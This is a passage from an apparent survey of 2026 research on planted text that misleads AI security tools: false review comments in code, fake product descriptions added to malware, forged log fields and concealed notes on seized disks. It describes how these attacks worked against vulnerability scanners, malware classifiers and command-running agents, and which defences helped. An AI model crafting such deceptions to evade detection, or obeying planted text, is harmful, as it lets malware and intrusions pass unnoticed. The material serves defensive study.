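Thornton, a cybersecurity professional, avoided the size problem by using short samples, typically 15 to 60 lines long. He wrote 100 programs in Python, JavaScript and Java, each with one vulnerability (a flaw that an attacker could exploit), and the model had to find it. The vulnerabilities were mistakes that an honest programmer could make, and the programs were not malware.

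Each program came in several versions with identical code but different comments, some accurate, some neutral and some misdescribing the code. The main comparison was between code without comments and code whose comments claimed it had already passed a security review, much like the comment in the 40-line script. Thornton tested five commercial models, including Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.2, and three open models. The commercial models found 89% to 96% of the flaws in the code without comments, and the open models found 53% to 72%.

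The misleading comments had little effect. The largest fall for any model was 4.1 percentage points, and the largest rise was 5. Each model saw the same programs with and without the comments, so Thornton could count the programs on which its answer changed. If comments have no effect, these changes should go in either direction about equally often. McNemar's test gives the probability that chance alone would produce a split at least as uneven as the observed one. Gemini 2.5 Pro missed four flaws that it had found in the bare code and found four that it had missed. DeepSeek Chat had the most uneven result, with one new miss and five new finds, and chance would produce a split at least that uneven about 22% of the time.

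This does not rule out a small effect on a single model. Thornton ran each combination once, and by his own calculation even five new misses with no new finds would fall just short of the usual standard of significance. The totals across all eight models, 48 new misses and 53 new finds, are more convincing, because comments that hid flaws should have produced clearly more misses than finds.

Thornton also tried more elaborate deceptions, such as detailed but fake review records, long comments that drew attention to harmless parts of the code, and false arguments that cited real security standards. He tested these on only 30 of the programs, whose flaws turned out to be easier to find than those in the rest. The commercial models still found more than 95% of the flaws. The extra sophistication did not help the attacker in this test, but the result might have been different with harder flaws.

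A warning in the prompt that comments were untrusted seemed to help somewhat. Among the commercial models, the false-review comments caused 14 new misses with an ordinary prompt, four with the warning, and ten with a third prompt that made the model trace data through the program in fixed steps.

### Thornton's four defences

Thornton then tested four automated defences on four of the commercial models. Overall detection rates were between 93.2% and 96.9% with the defences and 92.5% without, but these figures are hard to compare because the defence runs seem to have covered several comment styles, including those that exist only for the 30 easier programs. One defence, which scanned for suspicious comments and warned the model about them, reached 95.1% overall but caught none of the flaws that the models had missed before.

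The number of recovered flaws is a better guide. Thornton counted 57 flaws that the model had missed earlier. Removing all comments recovered 17 of them. Reviewing each program twice, with and without comments, and accepting an alarm from either review recovered 20. The best defence recovered 27 by giving the model the findings of a static analyser, ordinary software that looks for known kinds of flaw.

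That last defence had an advantage it would not have in practice, because Thornton had confirmed beforehand that static analysers could detect every flaw in his collection. The model in effect received the answer and only had to agree with it. In ordinary use, analysers miss some flaws and raise false alarms. Thornton did not measure false alarms for any of the defences, and a method that accepts an alarm from either of two reviews will normally produce more of them than a single review would.

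He advises against removing comments, mainly because DeepSeek Chat's detection rate fell from 93% to 89% when he did so. But the model also scored 89% on the bare code in the main experiment, and he had already found the gap between these two scores compatible with chance. Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.2 both did slightly better without the comments. On this evidence, the case against removal is weak. Cloudflare recommends removal but reports no test of it.

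### Task, model and style of comment

On short files the two studies mostly agree. Twenty comments did not lower detection of Cloudflare's scripts under 500 KB, and false reviews did not lower detection in Thornton's programs. The main discrepancy is non-frontier model 1. Its being a cheap model is probably not enough to explain its losses, because Thornton's weakest model, which found only 53% of the flaws in bare code, was no easier to mislead than the best one. The difference may be that Thornton's models always received the whole program.

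A model can check a comment more easily when looking for code flaws than when judging whether a script is malware. Many of the code flaws in Thornton's study are visible in a few lines, so a model that recognises one doesn't need to rely on the comment. A malware verdict often depends on the script's purpose. Many legitimate installers download and start a second program, just as the 40-line script does, so a comment about who wrote the script and why could carry more weight. By this reasoning, malware verdicts should be easier to sway than Thornton's results suggest, but neither study compared the two tasks.

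Both studies also used comments that the researchers had written in advance. Wu and Nita-Rotaru (2026), in a separate study also called *ALIBI*, instead used a language model as the attacker. After each failed attempt, the model read the detector's explanation of its verdict and revised the comment, using ten different styles and up to five rounds. The study tested four vulnerability detectors on 125 C and C++ functions that might use an invalid pointer. The attacker reversed between 91% and 100% of the detectors' correct verdicts, while one fixed comment claiming that the pointer was valid reversed between 3% and 17%.

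Repeated attempts explain much of that gap. The most effective single style reversed about 37% of the verdicts on the first attempt, but the attacker could try up to 60 times and needed to succeed only once. The type of flaw also favoured the attacker, because whether a pointer is valid often depends on code elsewhere in the program that the detector can't see. The detectors also ran on small or fairly old models, the strongest of which was GPT-4o.

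Warning the detectors to distrust comments helped much less here than in Thornton's test. Three of the four detectors still gave the wrong verdict in more than 90% of cases. When a second model removed uncheckable comments before the detector read the code, the attack succeeded less than 3% of the time, although the attacker had no chance to adapt its comments to this filter.

A comment can mislead a model without making a believable claim. Sun, Oprea and Wong (2026), in *Syntax- and Compilation-Preserving Evasion of LLM Vulnerability Detectors*, used an optimisation algorithm to find strings of characters that push a model towards a benign verdict. Placed in comments, these strings reversed 92% of one open model's correct verdicts, while random text of the same length reversed 13%. They reversed 65% of GPT-4o's verdicts but only 18% of GPT-5-mini's, so their effect depends heavily on the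 model. A much cruder comment that imitated the detector's output worked in 55% to 99% of cases, depending on the model.

These results are also relevant to Cloudflare's bypass zone. Sun and colleagues found that longer functions were, if anything, slightly less affected, even though the strings took up a smaller share of them. The opposite would be expected if planted text worked better when it made up a smaller share of the code. However, the functions were at most about 4,000 tokens long, so this is weak evidence about scripts of several megabytes. Removing comments stopped the comment-based attack completely, and it led one model to find 8.6% more flaws in code that nobody had tampered with.

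Text around the code can also influence a model. In *Words Speak Louder Than Code*, Shahriar, Cai and colleagues (2026) gave eight models the same code while varying the author information, the task wording or the results of an earlier scan. They compared a reassuring version of each with an alarming one and put the average effect at 18% for author information, 24% for the earlier scan and 33% for task wording. An attacker cannot control how the operator words the task but can often forge an author's name or a scan report. Using such forgeries, the researchers suppressed up to 97% of the flaws that a model had previously detected. In a malicious package, the equivalent text would be the author field, description and accompanying documents, which a cleaner that removes only code comments would leave in place.

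False authority was also the most effective simple attack in *LongPIBench* (Liu, Jia and colleagues, 2026), which tests planted text in long documents. In one task, a model decides whether to approve a change to a program. GPT-4.1 approved 27% of the changes with no planted text, at most 41% with conventional planted instructions, and 86% with a message falsely attributed to a senior engineer. Against the newer GPT-5.6, false authority succeeded 61% of the time across all four of the benchmark's tasks, compared with 8% for documents with no planted text.

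Thornton's invented sign-offs had no such effect, and the question put to the model is a likely reason. A senior colleague's opinion might properly count when deciding whether to approve code, but it has no bearing on whether the code contains a flaw. Length may be another reason. Liu and colleagues varied the amount of harmless text separately and found that many defences got worse as the input grew, though they could not tell whether dilution or the position of the planted text was responsible. Cloudflare could therefore still be right that comments work better in long files, even though its own figures don't establish it.

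A stock comment about an earlier review would probably do little to disguise the 40-line script, because the script is short and a competent model can work out what it does. An attacker who can read the scanner's reasons and try again, as publishers on ClawHub can, has a much better chance of evading detection. Wu and Nita-Rotaru's attacker relied on the same kind of feedback. A marketplace could publish the verdict but not the explanation. Attackers could still test one comment after another, but they would no longer learn which part of the model's reasoning to counter.

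## Experiments with false product descriptions in compiled programs

Compilers discard comments, so an attacker has to put a false description of a compiled program in its strings or metadata for a model to read it. Choi and colleagues published the main test of such descriptions in September 2026. They took working malware and added text that described it as part of a legitimate security product and gave innocent reasons for its suspicious behaviour. They did not change the malware's code, and the text contained no instructions to the model.

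### How the test worked

The researchers took 50 malicious Windows programs and 40 malicious Linux programs from MalwareBazaar, a public malware collection. An evidence builder extracted each program's metadata, section details, imported functions and printable strings. Gemini 2.5 Pro, GPT-5.5 Pro and Claude Opus 4.7 each judged each program in a single call from this evidence alone, without a sandbox record or the result of a signature check. They answered benign, unknown, suspicious or malicious and gave a confidence score between 0 and 1.

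Gemini called 35 of the 50 unmodified Windows programs malicious. Choi and colleagues used only these 35 in their later Windows comparisons. With N(malicious) for the number of programs called malicious before the change and an arrow for a change of verdict, the formulas for their strict and soft rates are:

Strict rate = N(malicious → benign) ÷ N(malicious)

Soft rate = N(malicious → benign, unknown or suspicious) ÷ N(malicious)

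For Windows the denominator is always 35. The "before" verdict is always Gemini's, even in the rates for the other two models.

Choi and colleagues also report the average drop in verdict, counting a change from malicious to suspicious as one step, to unknown as two and to benign as three. Readers can use these averages and the two rates to work out every model's verdicts on the modified programs.

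| Model | Malicious | Suspicious | Unknown | Benign | Strict rate | Soft rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 4 | 1 | 0 | 30 | 85.7% | 88.6% |
| GPT-5.5 Pro | 10 | 22 | 3 | 0 | 0% | 71.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 20 | 15 | 0 | 0 | 0% | 42.9% |

A pipeline that cleared every file Gemini labeled benign would have let through 30 of the 35 samples. With either of the other two models, it would have let through none, although with only 35 samples the true rate could still be as high as about 10%. Where the verdict stayed malicious, stated confidence fell by an average of 0.074 for GPT-5.5 Pro and 0.019 for Claude. Drops this small would matter mainly in a pipeline that blocks files only above a set confidence.

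### Stories that fit the malware

Gemini's verdict depended heavily on how well the story explained the malware's behaviour. Choi and colleagues tested three kinds of story on the same 35 programs. Gemini called 14 benign when the text presented the malware as an academic sample, which doesn't explain why a program would capture the screen or read the clipboard. A story about authorised security testing raised this to 18, and the security-product story raised it to 29. Real security products do monitor other programs and report to a server, so the security-product story plausibly explains much of what spyware does. The full attack, which also altered metadata to match the story, fooled Gemini on only one more program.

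The Linux samples mostly resembled botnet malware for small networked devices, whose behavior is harder to explain as that of a security product. Gemini called 16 of the 40 benign, while GPT-5.5 Pro gave one non-malicious verdict and Claude gave three. Gemini may have missed some of its 16 even without the false descriptions, because these rates cover all 40 programs and the researchers don't report how many each model had called malicious before the descriptions were added.

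The changes also affected conventional antivirus software. Windows Defender detected 39 of the 50 Windows programs before the modification but missed ten of those afterward. Choi and colleagues attribute this to the added material disturbing the features that Defender matches, since Defender does not interpret the false description. An operator who relies on antivirus software to catch the model's mistakes should therefore not assume that the two fail independently.

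### Why defences against instructions don't help

Choi and colleagues also tried planting conventional instructions to return a benign verdict, but Gemini did not return one for any of the 35 programs. This is the study's clearest evidence that resisting commands and resisting false claims are different abilities, because the model, the samples and the text's location were the same in both tests.

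A false explanation doesn't conflict with the operator's prompt, so training a model to favour the operator does little against it. *When AI Investigators Cannot Trust Their Tools* (2026), a study of agents whose tools return plausible but wrong data, makes the same argument about defences that look for instructions. Delimiters that mark the sample as untrusted data don't solve the problem either, because the model is supposed to draw conclusions from that data.

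Commands can still work. In *MARS*, Choi, who also led the study above, added instruction-like text to the stored evidence for malware. Across three models, this caused no clear fall in detection when the model gave its verdict directly. But when Gemini 2.5 Flash listed the program's behaviours for ordinary software to score, the pipeline lost its alerts on 28 of the 44 malicious programs it had flagged without the added text. The same text removed none of GLM-5.2's 64 alerts.

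### What GPT-5.5 Pro thought before the attack

The 71.4% soft rate for GPT-5.5 Pro counts every non-malicious verdict on programs that *Gemini* had called malicious, so it includes any program that GPT-5.5 Pro would have called suspicious even without the added text.

The study's table of confidence scores allows a partial check because it counts the programs on which each model's verdict stayed the same. GPT-5.5 Pro rated nine programs suspicious both before and after the change. If all nine are among the 35, the text lowered its verdict on at most 16 programs, not 25. GPT-5.5 Pro would then have called at most 26 of the 35 malicious before the change, so its soft rate against its own earlier verdicts would be at most 62%. Claude rated only one program suspicious both times, and the same calculation gives at most 14 out of 34, or 41%.

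The table doesn't make clear which programs it covers. It lists one program that Gemini rated suspicious both times, which can't be one of the 35 because Gemini had rated all of those malicious. However, GPT-5.5 Pro rated ten programs in the table malicious both times and Claude rated 20, the same numbers that they ended up rating malicious among the 35. The nine suspicious programs therefore probably belong to the 35, and the published 71.4% probably overstates the effect of the text.

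Baselines may well differ between models. Sava and colleagues gave eight models the same instructions and the same limits on how much code they could read, and some escalated only a few files while others escalated or flagged many more. A soft rate is hard to compare across models unless each has its own baseline.

Calling each model only once adds more uncertainty. In *MARS*, Choi ran three models ten times each on 30 unaltered Windows programs, 15 of them malicious. Gemini 2.5 Flash returned the same verdict all ten times for 13 of the malicious programs, but GLM-5.2 did so for only six and DeepSeek V4 Pro for five. Sava and colleagues found more agreement when they ran a cheap Gemini model three times. It gave the same verdict each time on 91% of files, and most of the disagreements involved the "suspicious" label. Some of the downgrades by GPT-5.5 Pro and Claude may therefore be ordinary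 variation between calls. A second call on the unmodified programs would have revealed this.

When Choi and colleagues repeated the attack, Gemini called 29 of the 35 programs benign, compared with 30 before, so variation between runs can't explain its result.

### A prompt that tells the model to distrust the sample

The researchers needed that repeat as a baseline for testing a defence. They rewrote the operator's prompt to warn Gemini that an attacker controls the strings, section names and metadata, and that any claim a file makes about itself should be verified. The new prompt did not mention false product descriptions, so they had not tailored it to their own attack. They ran the old and new prompts at the same time on the 35 modified programs.

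With the new prompt, Gemini's benign verdicts fell from 29 to 15, its malicious verdicts rose from four to 13, and its suspicious or unknown verdicts rose from two to seven. Fourteen programs got a benign verdict only with the old prompt, and none did only with the new one. If the two prompts were equally likely to produce a benign verdict, a split this uneven would occur by chance about once in 8,000 tests.

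The warning clearly helped, but Gemini still cleared 43% of the 35 malware samples it had recognised before the attack. (With so few samples, the true figure could be from about 28% to 59%.) This is probably because the prompt told the model to verify claims without giving it the means. The researchers had written the false description to be plausible, and Gemini could judge it only on plausibility because the evidence builder supplied the supposed maker's name but no signature-check result and no record of what the maker's real products look like.

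Claude sometimes did better with the same limited evidence. When it kept its malicious verdict, it often described the false product description itself as suspicious, because legitimate products rarely contain text defending them to analysts. Its explanations also compared the program's imports with what the claimed product would need. However, a written explanation may not reflect how a model reached its verdict. Claude also still rated 15 of the 35 only suspicious. Choi and colleagues did not test the new prompt on Claude or GPT-5.5 Pro.

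They also tested the prompt only on malware, so it may simply have made Gemini more likely to flag any program as malicious, and its false-alarm rate is unknown. Genuine security products are the most obvious concern, because they truthfully make the kinds of claims that the model is prompted to doubt.

In some other settings, operators can remove the misleading text. *When AI Agrees Too Much* (2026) reports that a misleading title or description on a proposed code change can lead a model to miss known vulnerabilities, and that removing this text recovered all the relevant missed detections. A code reviewer can still read the code without a description, but a malware pipeline that removed every name and string would lose much of its evidence.

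### Checking the claims with ordinary software

Choi and colleagues propose a stronger remedy, in which the evidence builder would check each claim before the model sees it and label it verified, unverified or contradicted. The model would then receive the claim and the result of the check as separate facts.

Suppose a Windows program's metadata names Larkfield Security, an invented company, as its maker. The evidence builder first looks for a digital signature in the part of the file reserved for one. To sign a program, a company computes a hash of it and encodes the hash with a private key. A certificate, issued by an organisation that Windows trusts, links the matching public key to the company's name. The evidence builder recomputes the hash and checks it against the signature. If an attacker has copied the signature from a real Larkfield program, or added text to a signed one, the hashes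 won't match.

The next two checks determine the label. The evidence builder compares the company named on the certificate with the one named in the metadata, and it consults a record of Larkfield's products. This record might list the products' usual file names, sizes and version formats, and whether Larkfield signs all its releases.

| What the evidence builder finds | Label | What the model can reasonably conclude |
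|---|---|---|
| A valid signature from Larkfield | Verified | Somebody with Larkfield's key signed this file |
| No signature, and no record of whether Larkfield signs its software | Unverified | The claim is no reason to trust the file |
| A valid signature from another company, or no signature although Larkfield signs everything | Contradicted | The claim is probably false, which is itself suspicious |

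A file name, size or version number that doesn't match the product record can contradict a claim, but a match proves very little because the attacker can change all three. Choi and colleagues' attack included metadata chosen to fit the claimed product. Only a valid signature, or a hash that matches a file the company is known to have released, should qualify a program for the verified label.

Even a verified label shows only who signed the program. Attackers steal signing keys and misuse genuine products, such as the flawed drivers that MANTLEMAZE exploits. The label is therefore evidence of who made the program, but the rest of the analysis must determine what the program does.

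The unverified label is the hardest to use well, because much legitimate software has no signature. The harmless Windows programs in *MARS* included unsigned open-source tools, and Linux programs are usually unsigned. Choi and colleagues suggest checking Linux files against package records and build identifiers, but a file separated from its package may match nothing. Treating every unverified claim as suspicious would send analysts many harmless files, so it would be better to give such claims no weight and require some other reason to pass the program.

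No certificate authority or product database can confirm that a program belongs to a student's research project or a private testing contract, so these claims would normally remain unverified. They were less effective than the security-product story, but Gemini still cleared 14 and 18 of the 35 programs because of them. *SEVRA-BENCH* (2026), a benchmark of deceptive code changes, distinguishes claims that a reviewer can check against the code from claims that depend on something outside it. A provenance check deals with outside claims about origin. To determine whether a program really captures the screen for technical support, a reviewer has to examine its code and the data it sends.

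Choi and colleagues did not test this remedy, and their evidence builder does not produce the fields it needs. All 35 modified programs would presumably have been marked unverified or contradicted, since the researchers did not have a key belonging to the company they imitated. It is less certain that Gemini would have changed its verdicts. A finding that a signature is missing gives a model more specific information than a general warning, but the model would still read the persuasive false description beside it. An operator who doesn't want to depend on how the model uses the finding can enforce the verification result in software after the model answers.

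The closest experiment, in Santos-Grueiro's *When Binaries Talk Back* (2026), concerns a different kind of false support. Several analysis tools may extract the same planted string from a program, so a report that combines their output seems to contain several independent pieces of evidence. Santos-Grueiro stored a record of each piece's origin outside the model, where no text in the sample could change it, and used a simple rule to count pieces with the same origin only once.

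The test used 16 harmless programs written for the purpose and two models, GPT-5.5 and DeepSeek-V3.2, which gave 32 cases. Without the origin records, the software accepted the false claim in all 32 cases. With them, it accepted none of the false claims and still accepted all 32 properly supported claims in a matching set. The reports and their citations were identical in both conditions, so the difference must come from the rule. A free-text field in the reports still repeated the false claim in all 32 cases, and Santos-Grueiro had to close this loophole by generating the final report from the checked claims alone.

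This is good evidence that origin records can block false support when ordinary software stores and applies them. But the false claims were all about what a program could do, and none were about who made it. The experiment also started with correct origin records, whereas checking a company's identity requires certificates and product records that may be incomplete.

### Evidence from other models and tasks

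The strongest figure in the ALIBI study, 30 out of 35, comes from Gemini 2.5 Pro, which is older than the two models it was compared with. The model's age may partly explain the result, but *MARS* suggests that other conditions matter too. Choi added benign-looking material to the stored evidence for malware and gave it to Gemini 2.5 Flash, Gemma 4 31B and GLM-5.2. The share of malware that these models flagged as suspicious or malicious fell by only 4.4 percentage points, with a plausible range of 1.5 to 8.1.

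Gemini 2.5 Flash is no newer than Gemini 2.5 Pro, so the use of newer models can't explain all of this difference. The material may have been less persuasive than a complete story fitted to the malware. The evidence in *MARS* also included signature data, which might have helped the models discount the material, but Choi did not test these two explanations separately.

A test from late November 2026 covers a newer model but a different task. In *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response*, Canale (2026) gave alerts from a simulated company network to Gemini 3.1 flash-lite and Gemini 4, and told both models in the prompt to treat every field as untrusted data. The models could close an alert as benign or leave it for an analyst. Fixed text that resembled instructions caused flash-lite to close one real attack but did not cause Gemini 4 to close any.

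Canale then had another model write text for the fields that an attacker controls, such as a command line or the reason given for an action. This model saw only the verdict and could try again. Flash-lite had already closed 19 of 46 attacks with no planted text. Of the other 27, it closed six after the first attempt and 15 within eight attempts. Gemini 4 had closed four of 28 with no planted text. It closed four of the other 24 after the first attempt and no more after three further attempts. The successful texts were false stories about authorised repairs and routine checks.

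Gemini 4 was therefore harder to mislead than flash-lite, but it was still misled in some cases when the prompt called the text untrusted. Its 17% can't be compared directly with Gemini 2.5 Pro's 86%, because Canale's attacker could write only in a few short alert fields, while Choi and colleagues had room for a detailed product description. Neither *MARS* nor Canale's study repeats the original attack on compiled malware with a current model.

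A fixed rule outside the model made the attacker less successful. When Canale let a model close an alert only if it stated at least 90% confidence and other software had scored the risk below a set limit, the attacker's success fell from 56% to 30% against flash-lite and from 17% to 8% against Gemini 4. In a complete pipeline, where the riskiest alerts went to analysts whatever the model concluded, the attacker hid none of the seven attacks it targeted. Gemini 4 closed two of the altered alerts, but both attacks had set off other alerts that the attacker could not reach. A triage pipeline that gives each file a single verdict lacks this backup unless its operator adds one.

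## Experiments with planted text in logs and seized disks

The alerts in Canale's simulated network came from logs, the records that servers and security tools keep of requests, logins and errors. An attacker can write into a log without putting a program on the victim's machine, but normally controls only a few fields in each entry. A suspect may have written almost everything on a seized disk. Researchers tested planted text in both settings in 2026. Some also gave the model tools, so the text could make it take an action as well as give a wrong verdict.

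### How an outsider writes into a log

A stranger can get text into a model's prompt through a company's logs without having an account, even when the company's software works as intended. Suppose the stranger types a sentence into the user-name box on the company's login page. The login fails because no account has that name, and the server records the time, the stranger's network address and the whole sentence as the attempted user name. When an analyst later asks a model to summarise the day's failed logins, the pipeline copies the entry into the prompt.

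The user agent, a line of text that browsers send with every request to identify themselves, offers the same opportunity because the sender can replace it with anything. Pandey and Bhujang (2026), in *Poisoning the Watchtower*, also list requested web addresses, the contents of requests and the domain names that a machine looks up. Error messages are another route because, as Shah (2026) points out in *LogJack*, many applications record the input that caused an error along with the error itself.

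Attackers forged log entries long before anyone gave logs to a language model. *Log Injection*, a page from 2019 or earlier by the web-security non-profit OWASP, explains how they do this when an application logs unchecked user input. Programmers can prevent it by escaping the input, which means altering characters such as line breaks so that the text stays in its field. Escaping protects the log's structure, but a model still reads the words inside the field.

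Log systems shorten, reformat or drop some fields before a model can read them. In *Poisoning the SOC*, Seymour catalogued the attacker-written fields that survive in a production log system and tested which ones influence the agents that read from it. The defender's software writes the rest of each entry, including the time and whether a login succeeded. An attacker who lies about the purpose of a request therefore still cannot easily change the server's record of its response.

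### Verdicts, summaries and recommendations

Pandey and Bhujang asked GPT-4o mini to label log entries, summarise them and recommend a response. They tested every combination of task, defence and type of planted text on 200 artificial entries, 120 of which recorded attacks such as attempts to break into a database. They planted the text in one randomly chosen field of each of those 120 entries.

Orders to ignore earlier instructions never got an attack labelled benign, and text disguised as encoded data failed at all three tasks. Two other types worked. False-authority text appeared to come from a member of the security team, and forged-structure text imitated the end of the log data followed by a finished verdict.

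| Job | Planted text | No defence | Fields marked as data | Marked fields and a word filter | Marked fields and fixed answers |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Label | False authority | 68% | 15% | 22% | 33% |
| Label | Forged structure | 17% | 17% | 22% | 16% |
| Summary | False authority | 49% | 44% | 35% | 24% |
| Summary | Forged structure | 96% | 75% | 27% | 38% |
| Recommendation | False authority | 34% | 11% | 21% | 20% |
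| Recommendation | Forged structure | 39% | 37% | 8% | 10% |

Pandey and Bhujang report that average attack success fell from 26.6% with no defence to 11.8% when the model's output had to match one of a few templates. Both averages include two types of text that hardly ever worked. For the other two types, success fell from about 51% to 24%, and the word filter did about as well.

Adding fixed answers made one result worse. When planted text claimed false authority, the model labelled 15% of attacks benign with marked fields alone and 33% with fixed answers as well. With 120 entries, chance is unlikely to explain the gap. Pandey and Bhujang think that having to choose between two labels made the model more likely to answer benign, but elsewhere they describe three labels, including "suspicious", so the cause is uncertain. If they are right, that is a reason to keep a middle verdict that leads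 to escalation.

Summaries were the weakest point. When the planted text used forged structure and no defence was in place, 96% of summaries left out the attack, played it down or accepted the false verdict. Almost none explicitly labelled the entry benign, so a program that searched for that label would have missed nearly all the failures.

The study did not test the same entries without planted text, so some of these failures could be ordinary errors. Such errors were probably rare, though, because the model labelled none of the entries containing the types of text that failed as benign. A bigger limitation is that the study covers only one small model from 2024. Pandey and Bhujang show how quickly such results go out of date. A simple simulation they built from earlier research predicted that orders to ignore instructions would hide 92% of attacks from an undefended model, but these orders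 hid none from the real model.

Karanjai, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *Context Contamination in LLM Analysis of Network Security Logs*, report much higher attack success rates. Their benchmark, LogInject, has 12,847 log entries, 2,569 of which contain planted text. They tested three production models against attacks meant to hide activity, raise false alarms, leak information or take over the output. Without defences, the attacks succeeded 83.4% of the time on average and up to 88.2%.

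Input filtering, a stricter prompt and output checks together cut successful attacks by 90.4%, but 8.4% of attacks still worked. Sending a request takes an attacker almost no effort, and if each attempt had an independent 8.4% chance of working, eight attempts would give roughly even odds of at least one success. However, hiding a whole intrusion may require misleading the model about many entries.

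Karanjai and colleagues also spread planted text across several entries, and this approach succeeded 76.4% of the time. Each fragment looks harmless on its own, so an operator would have to filter the assembled prompt as well as the individual entries.

LogInject reports an 83.4% success rate, which is hard to reconcile with Canale's results, where fixed text resembling instructions hardly ever worked. Canale's prompt warned the models that every field was untrusted, while LogInject's figure comes from models without defences. Canale also counted an attack as successful only if the model closed the alert. Two of the four attack aims in LogInject, raising false alarms and taking over the output, don't require the model to overlook an attack and may be easier to achieve.

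The amount of other text also matters. Emerging Evaluations Project's *The blind sentinel* tested a pipeline that searches stored log entries and gives the model only those that seem relevant to the analyst's question. The researchers planted text in a browser identifier and counted an attack as successful if the summary included an email address the attacker had supplied. They ran each of five small open models 50 times in each of nine conditions.

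| Entries in the log | One planted entry | One planted entry disguised as a security event | Several planted entries |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 60.4% | 55.6% | 13.6% |
| 50 | 0% | 0% (search never selected it) | 14.0% |
| 100 | 0% (search never selected it) | 0% | 1.2% |

The overall success rate was 16.1%, but the conditions differ so much that the average is not very informative. Four conditions had a success rate of zero. In two of them, the search never passed the planted text to a model, so the results don't show whether the models would have resisted it. In the other two, the text reached the model every time and no model followed it. The disguised entry got through the search with 100 entries but not with 50, which suggests that chance details of the logs affected the results.

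Still, the high rates with 10 entries matter in practice because analysts often narrow a search to a few suspicious events, which removes the ordinary entries that might have diluted the planted text. Repeating the text made the attack less successful in these small logs. Cloudflare found a similar effect in scripts, where some models were more likely to flag a script as suspicious when comments were repeated hundreds of times.

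### Agents that can run commands

Shah tested an agent that reads cloud logs to find faults and can run commands to repair them. Shah's test set, LogJack, contains 32 logs and reports with planted commands and ten harmless ones. Eight models worked on each item five times, and the test software recorded their commands without running them. In the main condition, Shah used a prompt telling the agent that it could investigate and fix problems, and in another, a prompt telling it to report its findings and fix nothing.

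| Model | Issued the planted command | Issued it when told to fix nothing | Issued any dangerous command | Issued one on harmless logs | Noticed the planted text |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 86% | 30% | 99% | 44% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 54% | 2% | 88% | 2% | 6% |
| GPT-4o | 53% | 0% | 63% | 2% | 9% |
| Qwen3 Coder Next | 33% | 1% | 41% | 0% | 9% |
| Devstral 2 123B | 16% | 0% | 58% | 4% | 10% |
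| Kimi K2.5 | 12% | 0% | 43% | 0% | 21% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 9% | 1% | 16% | 18% | 80% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0% | 0% | 19% | 0% | 72% |

Telling the agent not to fix anything worked well for every model except Llama, which still issued the planted command in 30% of runs. The agent still had its tools in these runs, so the protection depended on the model following the instruction. An operator who only wants a report can remove the tools.

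The two Claude models noticed most of the planted text but still issued some dangerous commands, which Shah attributes to the text's influence. That is plausible for Sonnet, which issued no dangerous commands on harmless logs. But Opus issued them slightly more often on harmless logs than on logs with planted text, so its results are not evidence that the text influenced it.

Planted commands are hard to reject because genuine logs also contain repair advice. GPT-4o ignored a blatant order in all five runs of one case, but in all five runs of another it followed a command presented as part of a standard repair procedure. Gemini 2.5 Pro once recognised part of a command as suspicious, removed a web address from it and issued the rest, which would have changed a setting in a live system.

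Commercial filters barely helped. Google's Model Armor detected none of the 32 planted texts and Microsoft's Azure Prompt Shield detected one, although both detected the same texts when they were presented outside the logs. Amazon's filter did not inspect the results of tool calls. Shah thinks the surrounding timestamps and error messages made the commands look like routine operations.

Shah wrote all the planted text and used simple pattern matching to decide which commands counted as dangerous. The agents could run any command, but many production agents have narrower tools, so Shah treats the rates as an upper limit on the harm.

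### Agents that take programs apart

According to *Challenges and Future Directions in Agentic Reverse Engineering Systems* (2026), most agents that analysts connect to reverse-engineering software work through Ghidra or IDA Pro, which disassemble and decompile compiled code. *Automatically Attacking Software Reverse Engineering AI Agents* (Crawford, Phillips and McClure, 2026) reports that text planted in small test programs led an agent connected to Ghidra to describe a completely different program. The attack worked against both Qwen3-8B and the much larger GPT-OSS-120B. The larger model found the text that one program really printed but did not use it in its conclusion. A human analyst would easily have spotted the planted text.

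In *Investigating Detection and Obfuscation of Prompt Injection Attacks*, Crawford and McClure (2026) tried to detect planted text in the output of analysis tools. Santos-Grueiro reports that they caught all 20 attacks in lists of strings but only 15 of 24 affected functions in decompiled code. A detector therefore needs testing on each kind of output the agent reads.

Santos-Grueiro tested whether planted text could make an agent request an unsafe action, using 20 test programs and the same two models as in the test of origin records. The models made unsafe requests in 35 of 40 cases with planted text and in none of 40 with clean versions of the programs. When the prompt marked the sample's content as data, the models still made 15 unsafe requests.

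Ordinary software then decided whether to allow each request. The model had to name a tool, its arguments, the purpose and the supporting evidence. The software checked these against a list of permitted tools, the analyst's permissions and resource limits. It refused any request for unrestricted command-line access, and any that used a program path or network destination chosen by the attacker. It blocked all 15 unsafe requests and approved all 40 matching requests from the analyst, but the models completed the analyst's task properly in only eight of those 40 cases.

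Success rates varied widely in this work too. In a broader test of four models without any protection, planted text achieved its aim in 38 of 480 cases (about 8%). In another test, which used output from real analysis tools, the planted text reached the model in all 32 sessions, but neither model requested the unsafe action, so the test provides no further evidence about the permission check.

Neither Santos-Grueiro nor Crawford and colleagues gave an agent a debugger, a tool that runs a program step by step. The risk would be greater with one, because a misled agent could let the malware run further than the analyst intended.

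### Three readers of the same disk

When police seize a computer, forensic examiners work on a copy of its disk. The suspect may have expected this and planted files for whoever reads it. Breitinger, Gruber and colleagues (2026) point out in *Prompt Injection Through Forensic Evidence* that the forensic software, the human examiner and the model all read the same disk. They use the term "perception gap" for a difference in what these three readers notice.

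In their scheme, content is visible if a reader would notice it in routine work, hidden if the reader handles it but cannot judge it, and unreachable if the reader cannot examine it. They give examples for software that extracts text and metadata but cannot read words in pictures, an examiner who looks at documents as they appear on screen, and a text-only model.

| Content | Software | Examiner | Model |
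|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary document text | Visible | Visible | Visible |
| White text on a white PDF page | Visible | Hidden | Visible |
| Metadata in a photograph | Visible | Hidden | Visible if the software extracts it as text |
| Words inside a picture | Unreachable | Visible | Unreachable |

White text on a white page is a good example of the danger, because the model reads it but an examiner who checks the page on screen sees nothing wrong. The table describes only one setup, and the results would change with other tools. An examiner who read the extracted text would see the white text too, and a model that accepts images could read the words in the picture.

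Breitinger and colleagues demonstrated three attacks on Gemma 4 12B, a small open model running on a local computer. The model read the disk through Autopsy, a forensic program, using 18 read-only tools. The planted notes were ordinary text files that were not concealed.

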